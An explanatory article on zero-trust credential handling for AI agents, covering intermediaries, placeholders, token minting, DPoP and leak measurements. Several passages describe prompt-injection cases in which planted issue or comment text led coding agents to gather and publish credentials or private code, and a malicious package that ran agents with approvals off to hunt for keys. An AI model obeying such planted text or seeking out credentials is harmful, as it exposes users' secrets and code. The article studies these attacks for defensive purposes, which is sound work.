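# Zero-trust credential design for AI agents: agents that hold no service credentials and are known only to an intermediary

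## Credentials, zero trust and the intermediary

Zero-trust credential design lets an AI agent use outside services without holding credentials for them. The agent sends its requests to a separate component, the intermediary, which identifies the agent, checks each request against a set of rules and adds the credential before forwarding the request. An attacker who takes over the agent can't copy credentials from it, but can still send requests through the intermediary for as long as the takeover lasts. The rules therefore matter about as much as keeping credentials out of the agent.

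### Agents, services and credentials

An agent is software in which a language model chooses actions and carries them out through tools, code or network requests. The Australian Cyber Security Centre's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026) distinguishes agentic AI from generative AI, which produces text or images for people to use. Agentic AI connects the model to other software so that it can plan and act without a person stepping in. *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026), a concept paper from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), describes a cycle in which the agent takes instructions, fetches more context based on them, processes the result, may act, and returns a response. The agent may fetch more context many times before it finishes.

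The example from here on is a coding agent that fixes bugs in one private repository, the store that holds a project's code and its history, on a code host such as GitHub. When someone assigns it a bug report, the agent reads the report and the code, edits files, runs the tests, pushes its changes to a separate branch and opens a pull request, which is a proposal that a human reviewer can accept or reject. The agent edits and tests the code on the machine where it runs. The branch and the pull request are stored on the code host, which is a service, meaning an outside system the agent uses. The language model is often a service too, with its own key.

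To open the pull request, the agent sends the code host a request over the network. Stripped down, it looks like this:

```
POST /repos/acme/billing/pulls HTTP/1.1
Host: api.codehost.example
Authorization: Bearer tok_8Kq2vX
```

The first line gives the action, and the second gives the service. The string at the end is the service credential, which is a key, token or password that a service accepts as proof of the right to act. It is the only part of those lines that identifies the requester to the code host. The code host looks up the string to find the account and its permissions, then either opens the pull request or refuses.

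*The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework* (Jones and Hardt, 2012), the internet standard for bearer tokens, defines a bearer token as one that any party holding it can use without proving possession of a cryptographic key. Any credential with that property, including a password or an API key, is a bearer credential. If someone copies one from the agent's machine, the copy works from anywhere until the credential expires or someone revokes it.

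An alternative is proof of possession, in which the client signs each request with a private key, so a copied token is useless on its own. But the service has to support it, and agent tooling mostly relies on bearer credentials. *Agent Authenticator* (Ganesan, 2026) cites an analysis of 5,205 open-source servers for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common interface between agents and tools. Of these, 88% require credentials and 53% rely on fixed API keys or personal access tokens. Only 8.5% use OAuth, a framework under which a service issues tokens with limited scope and lifetime. Ganesan points out that even OAuth tokens are bearer tokens by default.

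### Why an agent is a bad place to keep a key

A coding agent usually inherits whatever credentials are in its developer's environment. Ganesan gives the example of an environment with an SSH key, a GitHub personal access token, a cloud profile and a package-registry token in a configuration file. The agent in this example needs only a small fraction of that access, enough to read one repository, push a branch and open a pull request.

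Ordinary programs hold keys too, and people mostly accept this because those programs do the same thing every day, so a nightly backup job that contacts a new address stands out. Hartman's (2026) Internet-Draft *Credential Broker for Agents (CB4A)*, a working document with a stated expiry of 30 September 2026, contrasts these fixed call patterns with agents, which decide for themselves which services to call. An agent might need to write to Slack for one task and administer GitHub for the next, so nobody can choose one narrow set of permissions in advance.

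Agents can also expose credentials in more places than conventional applications do. Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026) observe in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* that a conventional application confines its secret to a secrets manager and a few trusted processes. An agent adds a persistent conversation, execution traces, messages to other agents and output that users can see, and a key that enters the model's context can be copied into any of them.

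An attacker can also steer the agent through prompt injection, which is text planted in material the agent reads that makes it follow the attacker's instructions. In a 2025 case that Ganesan documents, an attacker filed an issue, the code host's form of bug report, in a public repository. An agent read the issue, followed the instructions in it, opened the user's private repositories and published their contents in a public pull request. The attacker didn't need to steal a token because the agent already held one that covered every repository the user could reach.

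The weakness arises because language models, as *Attestation is All You Need* (2026) puts it, do not inherently separate trusted instructions from hostile content in the data. An operator's orders and a stranger's bug report both arrive as text. Developers have tried to separate the two with special formatting and filters. These help somewhat, but Kenney and colleagues cite a benchmark of ten defences in which none proved robust.

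An agent can also leak credentials with no attacker present. A trade-press account, *A missing config file triggered an AI agent to leak passwords* (Udinmwen, 2026), describes a coding assistant doing a routine code review. It could not find its configuration file, so it read all the variables set on the machine and leaked live passwords in the process.

An agent is compromised when its actions no longer serve its operator. The cause may be planted text, malicious code or the agent's own misjudgement, but this makes little difference to the design. Ganesan argues that the agent's own safeguards will not reliably catch a compromise, because agents start subprocesses that those safeguards do not observe and because agents act at machine speed with no person checking each step. It therefore seems wiser to plan for compromise than to count on preventing it.

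### What zero trust asks for

Zero trust, an approach to network security that predates AI agents, starts by planning for compromise. Organisations used to defend the perimeter of their internal network with a firewall, and anyone inside it, whether a logged-in user or an intruder, could reach a broad range of systems. The standard account of zero trust is *Zero Trust Architecture* (NIST Special Publication 800-207), by Rose, Borchert and colleagues (2020). It traces the idea from a US defence project called "black core" and the Jericho Forum, which in 2004 publicised the case against relying on perimeters, to John Kindervag, who coined the name at the research firm Forrester.

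Four of its principles carry over to agents:

- Network location earns no trust. A request from inside the organisation's network has to meet the same security requirements as one from outside.
- Access depends on a decision about the particular request. Having logged in once does not make everything afterwards valid.
- Least privilege applies: a subject gets the minimum access that its task needs.
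- The defender assumes a breach, and designs as if an attacker were already on the network.

Rose and colleagues define zero trust in terms of "least privilege per-request access decisions", but one of their seven tenets grants access per session and allows that the requester may have been checked only "sometime recently". A delay between the check and the request is tolerable for a person at a laptop. But an agent can read a hostile bug report forty minutes into a session and behave differently from then on, which is a good reason to decide access for each request.

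Rose and colleagues divide access checks between two components. The policy decision point decides whether to allow a request. The policy enforcement point sits in the traffic path and opens, monitors and closes the connection accordingly. They compare this to an airport, where passengers go through a security checkpoint and everyone in the boarding area beyond it counts as trusted. They call that area the implicit trust zone, and advise making it as small as possible by moving the checkpoint closer to whatever it protects.

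An agent with a working key in its environment is already inside the trust zone, which covers everything the key opens. The check took place once, when somebody issued the key.

Rose and colleagues wrote before today's agents existed, but their "subjects" include applications and other non-human entities, so the principles apply to agents in principle. How to apply them is less settled. In February 2026, Booth and colleagues were still asking the public how zero trust should govern what agents may do, and how to establish least privilege for an agent "when its required actions might not be fully predictable". Deployed systems were further behind. Red Hat's *Zero Trust for autonomous agentic AI systems* (2026) describes deployments in which agents prove who they are with a fixed ID and secret, the tools they call sometimes share one API token with broad access, and each component trusts the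 next because the one before it did.

### The design in four moves

The design answers these problems by taking the credential away from the agent and putting a checkpoint between the agent and the service.

1. The agent holds nothing that a service accepts. It has either no credential or a placeholder, a false credential that the intermediary later replaces. In the pull-request example, the string after "Bearer" becomes a dummy that the code host would reject. This applies the assumption of breach: whatever an attacker can read out of the agent is worthless at the service.

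2. The agent identifies itself to the intermediary. It might present a session token, which identifies one run of the agent and which no service accepts, or a workload identity, a cryptographic identity issued to a running program after checks on where and how it runs. This applies the rule that network location earns no trust. Malicious code can run on the same machine as the agent, so an intermediary that answered every local caller would be repeating the mistake of the old perimeter.

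3. The intermediary decides. Its policy decision point looks at which agent is asking, for what action, on which resource. A pull request in the billing repository passes. A request to read any other repository fails, even where the real credential would have allowed it. This applies the decision for each request, and least privilege with it.

4. The intermediary adds the real credential, forwards the request to the service and passes the response back. Here the intermediary acts as the policy enforcement point, and applies the rule in SP 800-207 that authorization comes before access. The credential travels from the intermediary to the service and never through the agent.

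Removing the credential altogether goes further than SP 800-207 (Rose et al.), in which the policy decision point can generate a credential for the client to use during a session. That is reasonable if the client keeps secrets well, but agents keep them poorly.

*Caging the Agents* (2026) sets out a security architecture for healthcare in which each agent runs in a container alongside a second container, called a sidecar, that holds all the keys for the model provider, code host, task tracker and cloud. The agent calls a local address, and the sidecar inserts the key, forwards the call and returns the answer. The sidecar also limits the rate, size and destinations of requests. An attacker who compromises the agent can use the sidecar's interface but does not get the keys. Kenney and colleagues describe a similar commercial product, in which the agent names only a "connector", such as the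 one for GitHub, and a trusted component outside the agent supplies the authentication for that connector's address.

The intermediary can be more than one program. Hartman separates the policy decision point from a credential delivery point, which fetches, issues or inserts the credential after approval. The decision point must never touch credentials, and the delivery point must never make policy decisions, so that an attacker who breaks into one does not gain the other's powers.

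Ganesan fairly objects that the secrets behind vaults and proxies are still bearer tokens, and that nobody has standardised the approach. Ganesan would rather give each agent a signing key, locked in secure hardware, for every service it uses. That would be stronger where services accept it, but Ganesan has not yet built a full implementation. For services that support none of the newer mechanisms, the proposal falls back on a broker that obtains an old-style token and keeps it from the model. An intermediary therefore looks hard to avoid for now, but using one does not settle what a compromised agent can order through it. This is a version of the confused-deputy problem, in which an attacker exploits a program's legitimate authority.

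### Earlier proxies for human users

Little of this design is new. Kenney and colleagues trace it to Saltzer and Schroeder, whose classic principles of computer security include least privilege and complete mediation, the rule that every access must be checked. The mechanism also has a history in software that spared people from typing passwords.

In *Trust-in-the-Middle*, Uzunay and Bicakci (2015) built an authentication proxy, a server that stores a person's passwords and submits them to websites. The person logs in to the proxy with a master password or a one-time password. When the person opens a website's login page, the proxy fills the fields with "dummy credentials". When the person clicks the submit button, the proxy decrypts the real username and password, puts them in place of the dummies and sends the page on to the website. The modern design is very nearly the same, with an agent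 in place of the person and an HTTP header in place of the login form. Uzunay and Bicakci also describe two earlier systems. One swapped placeholders for real keyboard input on the user's own machine. The other, a proxy called Delegate, applied rules and asked for extra credentials by mobile phone before a sensitive operation.

Uzunay and Bicakci assumed that the software on the user's side was not compromised, and they set aside attacks that hijack a session after login. With an agent on the user's side, that assumption is no longer safe, and misuse of an approved session becomes a central worry. People still have to trust a proxy that holds everyone's passwords, which is the problem Uzunay and Bicakci concentrated on. They suspected that this was the main reason such proxies had never been widely used.

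## How credentials leak from agents and what removing them changes

### Listing what the agent can reach

Moving an agent to this design starts with listing every credential it can reach. The list is usually longer than intended, because the agent can read whatever its user account can read.

| Where to look | How a key gets there |
|---|---|
| Environment variables | A start-up file such as `.bashrc` sets them for every program the user runs |
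| Configuration files | A developer saves a key in a `.env` file, or a tool writes one into its own settings |
| Shell history and temporary files | Someone types a key into a command, or a script saves one and never deletes it |
| Process memory and arguments | A program receives a key on its command line, where other programs can read it |
| Prompts | A user pastes a key into the conversation |
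| Tool output | A command prints a key, and the agent's framework adds the output to the conversation |
| Logs | The framework saves the conversation with any keys in it |
| Cloud metadata address | A cloud machine issues tokens for its own account to programs that request them |

Credentials can leak through configuration files. Ganesan cites a 2026 survey of public GitHub repositories that found 24,008 secrets in MCP configuration files, 2,117 of them still valid. Software can also write credentials into configuration files automatically. *GitInject* (2026), which examines agents in automated build pipelines, describes a standard step that copies a repository onto the build machine and writes the repository token into `.git/config`. Anyone can reverse the token's encoding, but a search for strings that look like tokens could easily miss it.

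Credentials can also leak through the conversation itself, which is easier to overlook. *Soei* (2026) analyses 45 agent sessions from one developer over five months and finds strings that looked like credentials in 16 of them. Of the 1,326 matching records, 44 were in the developer's prompts, 654 in the agent's messages and 628 in the arguments the agent passed to tools. The matching was loose, and only 208 records were high-confidence matches, from five distinct tokens. Still, a key that enters the conversation once tends to reappear.

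A key can end up in an agent's transcript without anyone pasting it in. In an example from *SlotGuard* (2026), an agent debugging a problem listed the running processes, and one had a key in its command line, so the key went into the transcript. *Cybersecurity AI (CAI) Dataset* (Mayoral-Vilches, 2026) describes 230,935 logged sessions from a security tool whose users routinely entered live credentials themselves, even though they knew the tool kept logs.

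It makes sense to inventory credentials from inside the agent's environment, under the same user account and with the same tools. The checks Kenney and colleagues used would serve as a template. They covered the names and values of environment variables, the file through which Linux exposes them, twelve common credential paths, folders where platforms mount secrets, and the Amazon and Google metadata addresses. Kenney and colleagues reported only counts and yes-or-no answers, which is a good habit because an inventory that prints the keys creates another copy of them. For each connection, they recommend recording the owner, provider, permissions, expiry date and how to replace the credential.

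### One key through five stages

Kenney and colleagues divide credential exposure into five stages. The code-host token from the pull-request example, `tok_8Kq2vX`, could pass through them like this:

1. Introduction: a developer saves the token in the project's `.env` file.
2. Propagation: the agent reads the file and the token enters the conversation. Copies then appear in the log, in the agent's long-term memory and perhaps in a test file that it writes.
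3. Trigger: a hostile bug report, a malicious tool response or an ordinary model error leads the agent to disclose or misuse the token.
4. Execution: someone uses the token's permissions, for instance to read another private repository.
5. Persistence: the token keeps working from the attacker's machine after the agent's session has ended.

The second stage can begin with reasonable behaviour. Docker, which sells a sandbox built on the design covered here, gives the example of an agent that is connecting a program to an outside API and opens `.env` to find the key's name. The agent sees the key's value too, and the value can then end up in a generated configuration file or a commit.

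Ganesan's account of the Shai-Hulud worm of 2025–2026 shows how much the last stage can matter. The worm stole tokens for GitHub and for npm, the main JavaScript package registry, and used them to publish itself inside packages its victims maintained. It could do this because npm accepted long-lived publishing tokens from any machine.

### How agent skills spread keys

The best measurements of propagation come from agent skills, packages of instructions and scripts that people install to give an agent new abilities. In *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) sampled 17,022 of the 170,226 skills on SkillsMP, a large marketplace. They searched the instructions and code for signs of credential handling and found 3,156 candidates. They ran each candidate in a sandbox containing fake keys, three times on an ordinary task and three times with hostile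 instructions in material it would read. Three researchers then reviewed the 1,427 skills that had behaved suspiciously.

Confirmed credential leaks appeared in 520 skills, or 3.1% of the sample, with 1,708 separate issues. Carelessness accounted for 437 of these skills and 1,371 of the issues. The other 83 skills were malicious.

Most of the careless issues came from debug logging. A developer prints a token to check that a login works, then forgets to remove the line. In an ordinary program, the token appears on the developer's screen and little else happens. But an agent framework captures whatever a script prints and puts it into the model's conversation. One Google Workspace skill printed both its access token and the refresh token used to obtain new ones. Chen and colleagues attribute 73.5% of vulnerabilities to this kind of logging, but that figure is a share of the careless issues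 (1,007 of 1,371). The share of all 1,708 issues is about 59%.

The researchers also classify 89.6% of the affected skills (466 of 520) as immediately exploitable, because they leaked credentials while running and needed no special privileges. Not all 466 leak on every use. In 237 of the affected skills, the leak appeared in at most one of the three ordinary runs but showed up when the researchers planted hostile text. The other 54 skills had keys written into their published code, which seems at least as easy to exploit.

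The 3.1% may not hold for other marketplaces. It could well be too low for this one, because the code analysis covered only Python and JavaScript and did not follow a key from one variable to another.

If the agent held only a placeholder, a forgotten print line would expose only the placeholder. A placeholder wouldn't help with the 107 skills whose developers had published their own keys. The owners have to revoke those keys, not just delete them, because the keys remained in more than 50 forks (independent copies of a repository) after they were removed from the original repositories.

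### How an attacker triggers the leak

Researchers distinguish attackers by how close they can get to the agent. The most constrained kind in *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026) is an outsider who can only alter material that the agent will later read. The paper describes this kind of attacker as highly realistic. Such an outsider could carry out the "Comment and Control" attacks, which the security engineer Aonan Guan disclosed in April 2026 with Zhengyu Liu and Gavin Zhong of Johns Hopkins University.

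SecurityWeek's *Claude Code, Gemini CLI, GitHub Copilot Agents Vulnerable to Prompt Injection* quotes Guan's account at length. The attacks worked against Anthropic's Claude Code Security Review, Google's Gemini CLI Action and GitHub's Copilot Agent, all running in GitHub Actions, which starts jobs automatically when something happens in a repository. The researchers put instructions into pull-request titles, issues and comments. The agents read these instructions, ran commands, collected credentials from their environment and published the credentials on GitHub, in one case disguised as a security finding. Only the Copilot attack required the victim to act, by assigning the attacker's issue to the agent.

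The stolen credentials left through GitHub, the code host, which a coding agent needs to reach. Restricting the agents' network access to GitHub would not have stopped the leak.

Guan blames the architecture, in which agents hold powerful tools and secrets "in the same runtime that processes untrusted user input". The vendors' fixes mostly did not change that arrangement. Google added warnings to the model's instructions. Anthropic blocked `ps`, a command that lists running processes. Guan told SecurityWeek that the attack still worked in principle if the attacker rewrote the text. GitHub called the problem a known architectural limitation. According to The Next Web's *Anthropic, Google, and Microsoft paid AI agent bug bounties, then kept quiet*, none of the three companies published a security advisory. Microsoft reported a similar exposure of pipeline secrets in another Anthropic product,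 the Claude Code GitHub Action.

Removing the key from the runtime closes every route to it, not just the one that blocking `ps` closes. The agents in these attacks could then have published a placeholder instead of the key, but they could still have published any private code they had permission to read.

An attacker who already has code on the machine can use the agent to search for credentials. On 26 August 2025, attackers published malicious versions of Nx, a JavaScript build package with about four million downloads a week. According to Docker, the installation script looked for three AI coding agents, started any it found with approval prompts switched off, and told them to list files likely to contain keys. GitGuardian, a company that scans for leaked secrets, counted 2,349 distinct stolen secrets, more than 1,100 of them still valid when it checked. The inventory therefore needs to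 cover the whole user account, not only the project the agent works on.

### Relying on the model's judgement

An alternative is to leave the credentials with the agent and trust the model to recognise when not to use them. *CredLeakBench* (Ahmed, Fioresi and colleagues, 2026) tested this on seven models. Each agent could open web pages and submit forms, and held made-up passwords and personal records for fictional services. In the two main tests, half of the scenarios led to a genuine sign-in page and half to a phishing page with one of eight warning signs, such as a misspelled domain or an unencrypted connection.

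In the first test (512 scenarios), the user supplied a link and asked the agent to sign in. In the second (256 scenarios), the user did not mention signing in, but asked the agent to sort through an inbox where the relevant message was mixed in with unrelated emails. The leak rate is the share of phishing runs in which the agent submitted any of the user's information. The false-refusal rate is the share of genuine runs in which the agent submitted no form, whatever the reason.

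| Model | Leaks, told to sign in | False refusals, told to sign in | Leaks, inbox | False refusals, inbox |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 31.2% | 6.6% | 1.8% | 88.3% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 19.9% | 13.7% | 1.8% | 63.8% |
| GPT-5-mini | 45.8% | 12.5% | 14.1% | 43.8% |
| Gemini 3.6 Flash | 40.6% | 0.1% | 9.4% | 54.7% |
| Qwen3.5-9B | 66.5% | 2.7% | 40.1% | 44.3% |

The two pairs of figures in the Opus 4.8 row come from different tasks, so the drop in leaks from 31.2% to 1.8% does not show the effect of a defence. Nobody in the inbox test had asked Opus to sign in anywhere, so it mostly didn't, whether the message was genuine or fake. Ahmed and colleagues also report balanced accuracy, which averages the share of phishing runs without a leak and the share of genuine runs with a submission. An agent that never signed in would score 50%. Opus's score fell from 81.1% to 54.9%, so it had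 become more reluctant to act and worse at telling genuine pages from phishing pages.

"False refusal" is a harsh term for some of these cases, since someone who asks for help with an inbox might prefer an agent that doesn't enter passwords on its own initiative. In a further test that combined phishing messages with real pending tasks, Opus escalated 722 of 768 cases and leaked nothing, but it also never completed the sign-in through the genuine site.

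Small changes in the user's wording also had large effects. When the user made a neutral request to sign in, Opus leaked credentials in 44.3% of phishing runs. When the user asked it to check the site first, the rate fell to 10.9%, but false refusals rose from 1.6% to 25.0%. The leak rate also depended on the warning sign. It was 9.4% when the domain was misspelled and 90.6% when the domain was right but there was no encryption.

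Information helped most models. When Ahmed and colleagues gave Opus the official domain and told it to compare that domain with the page's address, leaks fell from 46.9% to 12.0% and false refusals from 18.8% to zero. Unencrypted pages made up one in eight phishing cases and could pass this comparison, so they probably account for most of the remaining leaks.

This seems like a good argument for moving the decision out of the model. Ordinary code can check that an address matches exactly and that the connection is encrypted, and the result doesn't depend on how the user phrases the request. An intermediary that ties each credential to one destination makes that check every time. It wouldn't prevent every leak in the benchmark, because the agents also gave away identity and financial details, which an agent may need to read to do its job.

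### What removing the key changes

Kenney and colleagues argue that the first two stages disappear "by construction" if no reusable credential enters the conversation or the environment where the agent runs. If the billing project's `.env` file holds a dummy value, the agent can copy it into the log, a test file and a public commit, and the code host will reject any copy that someone tries to use.

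The trigger stage remains because the hostile bug report still reaches the model. The execution stage also remains because the agent can try to open a pull request containing private code through the intermediary, which will add the real token if the rules allow the request.

Persistence is harder to classify because keeping the key in a vault only partly addresses it. An attacker who controls only the agent no longer gets a copy to use elsewhere, but the token in the vault may still last for years, and Kenney and colleagues say that custody alone does not address persistence. Their risk rating for the replay of long-lived tokens falls from 20 to 8 out of 25. Their rating for prompt injection falls from 25 to 12, and for a connection with too many permissions from 20 to 15. These ratings are judgements of likelihood multiplied by judgements of impact, not measurements.

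They did test whether the key stays hidden. On 27 September 2026 they ran two experiments on Corvic Security Vault, their employer's product and the connector system described earlier, using code inside its sandbox. One experiment used a connection to GitHub and the other a connection to FRED, an economic data service. The researchers ran 16 checks and wrote down the expected result of each beforehand. All 16 came out as expected:

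- A request to GitHub succeeded as an authenticated user, although the code that sent it contained no credential.
- None of the sandbox's 20 environment variables contained a recognisable key, and none of the twelve common credential files existed.
- Three websites that send back whatever they receive showed no sign of the credential.
- OpenAI's API, an unrelated service, replied that the request had no authentication.
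- The Amazon and Google metadata addresses did not respond within six seconds.

The successful GitHub request matters because a sandbox with no network access would have passed most of the other checks. FRED rejected its request because the vault put the key in a header instead of the web address, where FRED expects it. This failure didn't expose the key, and the researchers scored it separately from the security results.

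The experiments used a fixed set of harmless requests, with no hostile text and no attempt to manipulate a model. Kenney and colleagues did not run a comparison without the vault, so the results can't show how much it reduces leaks. They did not repeat the trials or test browser tools, redirects to other addresses, or a malicious service at the approved address. They also did not verify the vault's encryption or its separation between customers. They suggest running an established prompt-injection benchmark against a system with a vault, which would replace some of their estimated risk ratings with measurements.

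Ganesan's review of incidents also suggests that removing credentials from agents has limits. Ganesan identifies four recurring failures: credentials that any local code can read, safeguards that run inside the agent, permissions that are too broad, and services that cannot tell an agent from its user. In Ganesan's view, vaults and proxies address part of the first.

Removing a key from the agent's environment also doesn't delete any copies in old logs and transcripts. When moving to the intermediary, the builder should therefore issue a new key and revoke the old one. Otherwise, the inventory will have to include every place the old key might have gone.

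### A fleet that had not yet removed its keys

*Caging the Agents*, cited earlier for its credential-holding sidecar, also includes an inventory from real use of nine agents at a healthcare technology company, each on its own virtual machine. The paper describes 90 days of progressively tighter security, but its dated milestones span about five weeks, from 3 February to 11 March 2026.

On 11 March an auditing agent with remote access to all nine machines reported four high-severity findings. The first was a `.bashrc` file that exported 12 credentials, including a GitHub token and keys for Amazon's model service. The second and third were on two machines where every user could read the configuration file that stores an agent's credentials. The fourth was an Amazon key in another machine's `.bashrc`. Six of the nine machines had no findings above low severity.

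The company fixed all four the same day by saving backups, deleting the exported keys, and restricting the files to their owner. These fixes were worthwhile but fell far short of removing the keys, because an agent that runs as a file's owner can still read it. *Caging the Agents* does not list replacing the keys among the fixes, and a backup of the first `.bashrc` would contain the same 12 credentials. Token files in two agents' working folders remained open findings of medium severity.

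The abstract describes the full architecture as "developed and deployed", but a later comparison of machine generations lists its main parts as the target of a migration:

| Control | In place by March 2026 | Planned |
|---|---|---|
| Credentials | Files that only their owner can read | A proxy that holds the keys |
| Outgoing connections | Domain filtering and logging | A list of allowed destinations for each agent |
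| Isolation | Separate user accounts | A sandbox between the agent and the operating system |
| Untrusted text | Written rules in each agent's instructions | Labelled content and structured sender details |

The claim in *Caging the Agents* that the proxy eliminates credential exposure is therefore a prediction about a system the company had not yet moved to.

The paper's claims about attacks should be read with similar care. It matches eleven case studies, from an earlier experiment in which researchers tried to misuse agents built on the same framework, to the layer of the architecture that should address each one. It counts nine as directly mitigated, but one of those nine is a case of agents helping each other solve a problem, which the paper's own table lists as needing no defence.

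The paper matches each defence to an attack, which gives a reason to expect the defence to work, but it reports no test that repeats an attack with the defence running. In one of the case studies, an agent disclosed 124 email records to someone who had no right to them. The paper's defence is to restrict outgoing connections and label untrusted text. If the person asked through a messaging service on the allowed list, the connection rules would let the reply through, and preventing the disclosure would depend on the model treating the labelled text as untrusted.

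## Choosing what the agent holds instead of a real credential

Once the old keys are out of the agent's environment, the builder has to decide what goes in their place. There are four options, listed here from the least to the most useful to a thief:

- nothing at all
- a placeholder, which the intermediary swaps for the real credential
- a short-lived token, meaning a real service credential that expires within minutes or hours
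- a long-lived key that the intermediary revokes after the task

An agent that holds nothing or only a placeholder has to send every request through the intermediary, while one that holds a token or a key can call the service itself, which is faster but riskier.

### When software needs a placeholder

Holding nothing works when the agent's tools already go through the intermediary, as with the GitHub connector that Kenney and colleagues tested.

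Much existing software expects a key, though. A client library often reads one from an environment variable when it starts, and stops with an error if the variable is empty. Some libraries also check that the key has the right prefix or length. Rewriting the library is rarely worth the trouble, so the builder gives it something harmless to read:

```
CODEHOST_TOKEN=tok_PLACEHOLDER
CODEHOST_URL=https://intermediary.internal
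```

The library accepts the token, and the URL directs its requests to the intermediary. Placeholders also help when an agent uses two accounts at the same service. Each account gets a different placeholder, which the intermediary uses to choose the credential to add.

The intermediary can't simply swap a false key for the real one if the client never sends its key. Clients for Amazon's cloud, for instance, use a secret key to sign each request and send the signature instead of the key. A signature made with a false key is invalid, so the intermediary has to sign the request again with the real one.

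Before relying on a placeholder, the builder should send it straight to the service and confirm that the service rejects it. If the same placeholder later appears among the service's failed logins, a request has bypassed the intermediary.

### Proxying, minting and wrapping

Hartman describes three models for a credential broker, another name for the intermediary. Proxying keeps the credential away from the agent, minting gives the agent a short-lived token, and wrapping gives it the long-lived key for a limited time.

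Hartman's draft is an individual proposal with no formal standing at the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which publishes internet standards, so it is more useful as a source of terms than as a specification to follow. Hartman posted version 00 on 29 March 2026 with an expiry date of 30 September 2026, and no later version or successor seems to have appeared. Sweeney's (2026) *Credential Delegation Protocol for AI Agents in Multi-System Environments*, a separate individual draft from July, also aims to hide OAuth tokens from agents.

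In proxying, which Hartman calls Model A, the agent sends its request with a session token. The proxy checks the token, adds the real credential, forwards the request and returns the response.

Proxying gives the strongest isolation of the three. The proxy can inspect, log and filter every request, and the service needs no special support. But each call takes two network hops instead of one, and the proxy can become a bottleneck or a single point of failure. Hartman adds that the proxy must understand the format of every service's requests. How much it must understand depends on the rules it enforces. It needs to understand very little to replace a header, but to let an agent open pull requests but not merge them, it must parse the code host's requests.

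Minting, or Model B, has more steps:

1. The agent fills in and signs a form that names the service, action, resource, permissions and lifetime it wants. Hartman's sample form asks for 60 seconds.
2. The policy decision point checks the agent's identity, the rules and the agent's usual behaviour. The form also has a field for a justification, which the decision point must ignore because a compromised agent could write a persuasive one.
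3. If the decision point approves, it sends a signed decision to the credential delivery point.
4. The delivery point fetches the long-lived credential, uses it to obtain a short-lived token and erases the long-lived credential from its memory.
5. The agent calls the service directly with the token.
6. The token expires. The agent can't renew it, and has to prove its identity again to get another.

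The large cloud platforms all support this, as does GitHub, which issues tokens to an installed app and limits them to particular repositories. The broker doesn't carry the traffic, and Hartman describes the approach as proven at massive scale. The main weakness is that the agent holds a real credential, if only briefly. The service also has to support minting, and its permission system limits how narrow the token can be. Hartman's sample form is a request to post in one Slack channel, `#engineering`, but the permission listed is `channels:write`, which doesn't specify a channel. If the service can't narrow that further, the token allows more than the decision point approved.

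A minted token can also be hard to cancel early. Hartman rates failed revocation as a high-severity threat because services cache earlier access decisions. Some tokens carry their own permissions and a signature, so a service can check them without asking the issuer. According to *NEBULA* (2026), a specification for refresh tokens, the structure of these self-contained tokens prevents immediate revocation. A short lifetime is therefore the main protection.

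Wrapping, or Model C, is for services that accept only long-lived keys:

1. The broker gives the agent the actual key.
2. The broker schedules the key's revocation for the end of the task or a fixed time limit.
3. The agent calls the service directly until the revocation takes effect.

Wrapping is simple and works with any service. But the agent holds a full-strength key during the task, and if revocation fails, the key stays valid indefinitely. Each task also needs its own key, since revoking a shared one would cut off every other program that uses it. Hartman calls wrapping the weakest model and advises against it for new integrations.

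Hartman writes in the overview that the agent "never holds real credentials", but that is true only of proxying.

### Measuring exposure in repository-days

A made-up example gives a sense of scale. Suppose the coding agent's key opens 40 repositories and has 90 days left when it leaks. A thief then has 40 × 90 = 3,600 repository-days of access. The same sum for the other options, assuming that each leak happens as soon as the agent receives the credential, gives:

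| What leaks | Repositories | Valid for | Repository-days |
|---|---|---|---|
| Long-lived key | 40 | 90 days | 3,600 |
| The same key, revoked after an hour | 40 | 1 hour | 1.67 |
| Short-lived token | 1 | 1 hour | 0.04 |
| Placeholder | 0 outside the intermediary | – | 0 |

Most of the improvement comes from the shorter lifetime. Cutting the lifetime from 90 days to one hour divides the exposure by 2,160, while cutting access from 40 repositories to one divides it by 40. With the 60-second lifetime in Hartman's sample form, the token's exposure would fall to about 0.0007.

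The figure for the revoked key depends on revocation working every time. If it failed once in every 100 tasks, the average exposure would be 0.99 × 1.67 + 0.01 × 3,600, or about 38 repository-days. That is more than 20 times the intended figure, nearly all of it from the one failure. Anyone who uses wrapping should test the key after each revocation instead of assuming that the scheduled revocation worked.

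This measure treats an hour as short, but a script can copy a repository in seconds, and the copy remains after the token expires. It counts a repository of test data the same as the billing code, and permission to read the same as permission to delete. It also ignores whether a token can create other credentials. A one-hour token that lets its holder add a new access key to the repository could lead to months of access.

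The measure also counts only one leak. An agent that stays compromised for eight hours can request eight one-hour tokens, for a total of 0.33 repository-days. With a placeholder, it could use the same repository through the intermediary for just as long. The zero in the table covers only use outside the intermediary, so the rules on permitted requests still matter.

### Tying a token to its holder

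A minted token would be less dangerous if, unlike a bearer credential, it required proof of possession of a private key. Such tokens are called sender-constrained. Hartman proposes using DPoP for this, a standard that Fett, Campbell and colleagues define in *OAuth 2.0 Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP)* (RFC 9449). DPoP involves the client (here the agent), the issuer that hands out tokens, and the service that accepts them.

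1. The client creates a pair of keys, one private and one public. It asks the issuer for a token and attaches a proof, which is a short message containing the public key and signed with the private key.
2. The issuer checks the proof and ties the token to the public key, for example by putting a hash (a digital fingerprint) of the key inside the token.
3. For each request to the service, the client signs a new proof. This proof covers the request's method and address, the time, a unique identifier and a hash of the token.
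4. The service checks the signature and each of those details. It also checks that the key in the proof is the one tied to the token, and refuses the request if anything doesn't match.

With DPoP, the pull-request call from earlier would look like this:

```
POST /repos/acme/billing/pulls HTTP/1.1
Host: api.codehost.example
Authorization: DPoP tok_5Rm9cT
DPoP: (signed proof)
```

The main contents of the proof, once decoded, would be:

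```
method:      POST
address:     https://api.codehost.example/repos/acme/billing/pulls
created:     10 December 2026, 09:46:40 UTC
identifier:  e7c1-04b9
token hash:  (hash of tok_5Rm9cT)
```

Someone who copies only `tok_5Rm9cT` can't produce the next proof. Copying the whole request also captures a proof, but it works only for that address and method, and only until the service stops accepting it, ideally within seconds or minutes. The service can also remember the identifiers it has seen and reject repeats.

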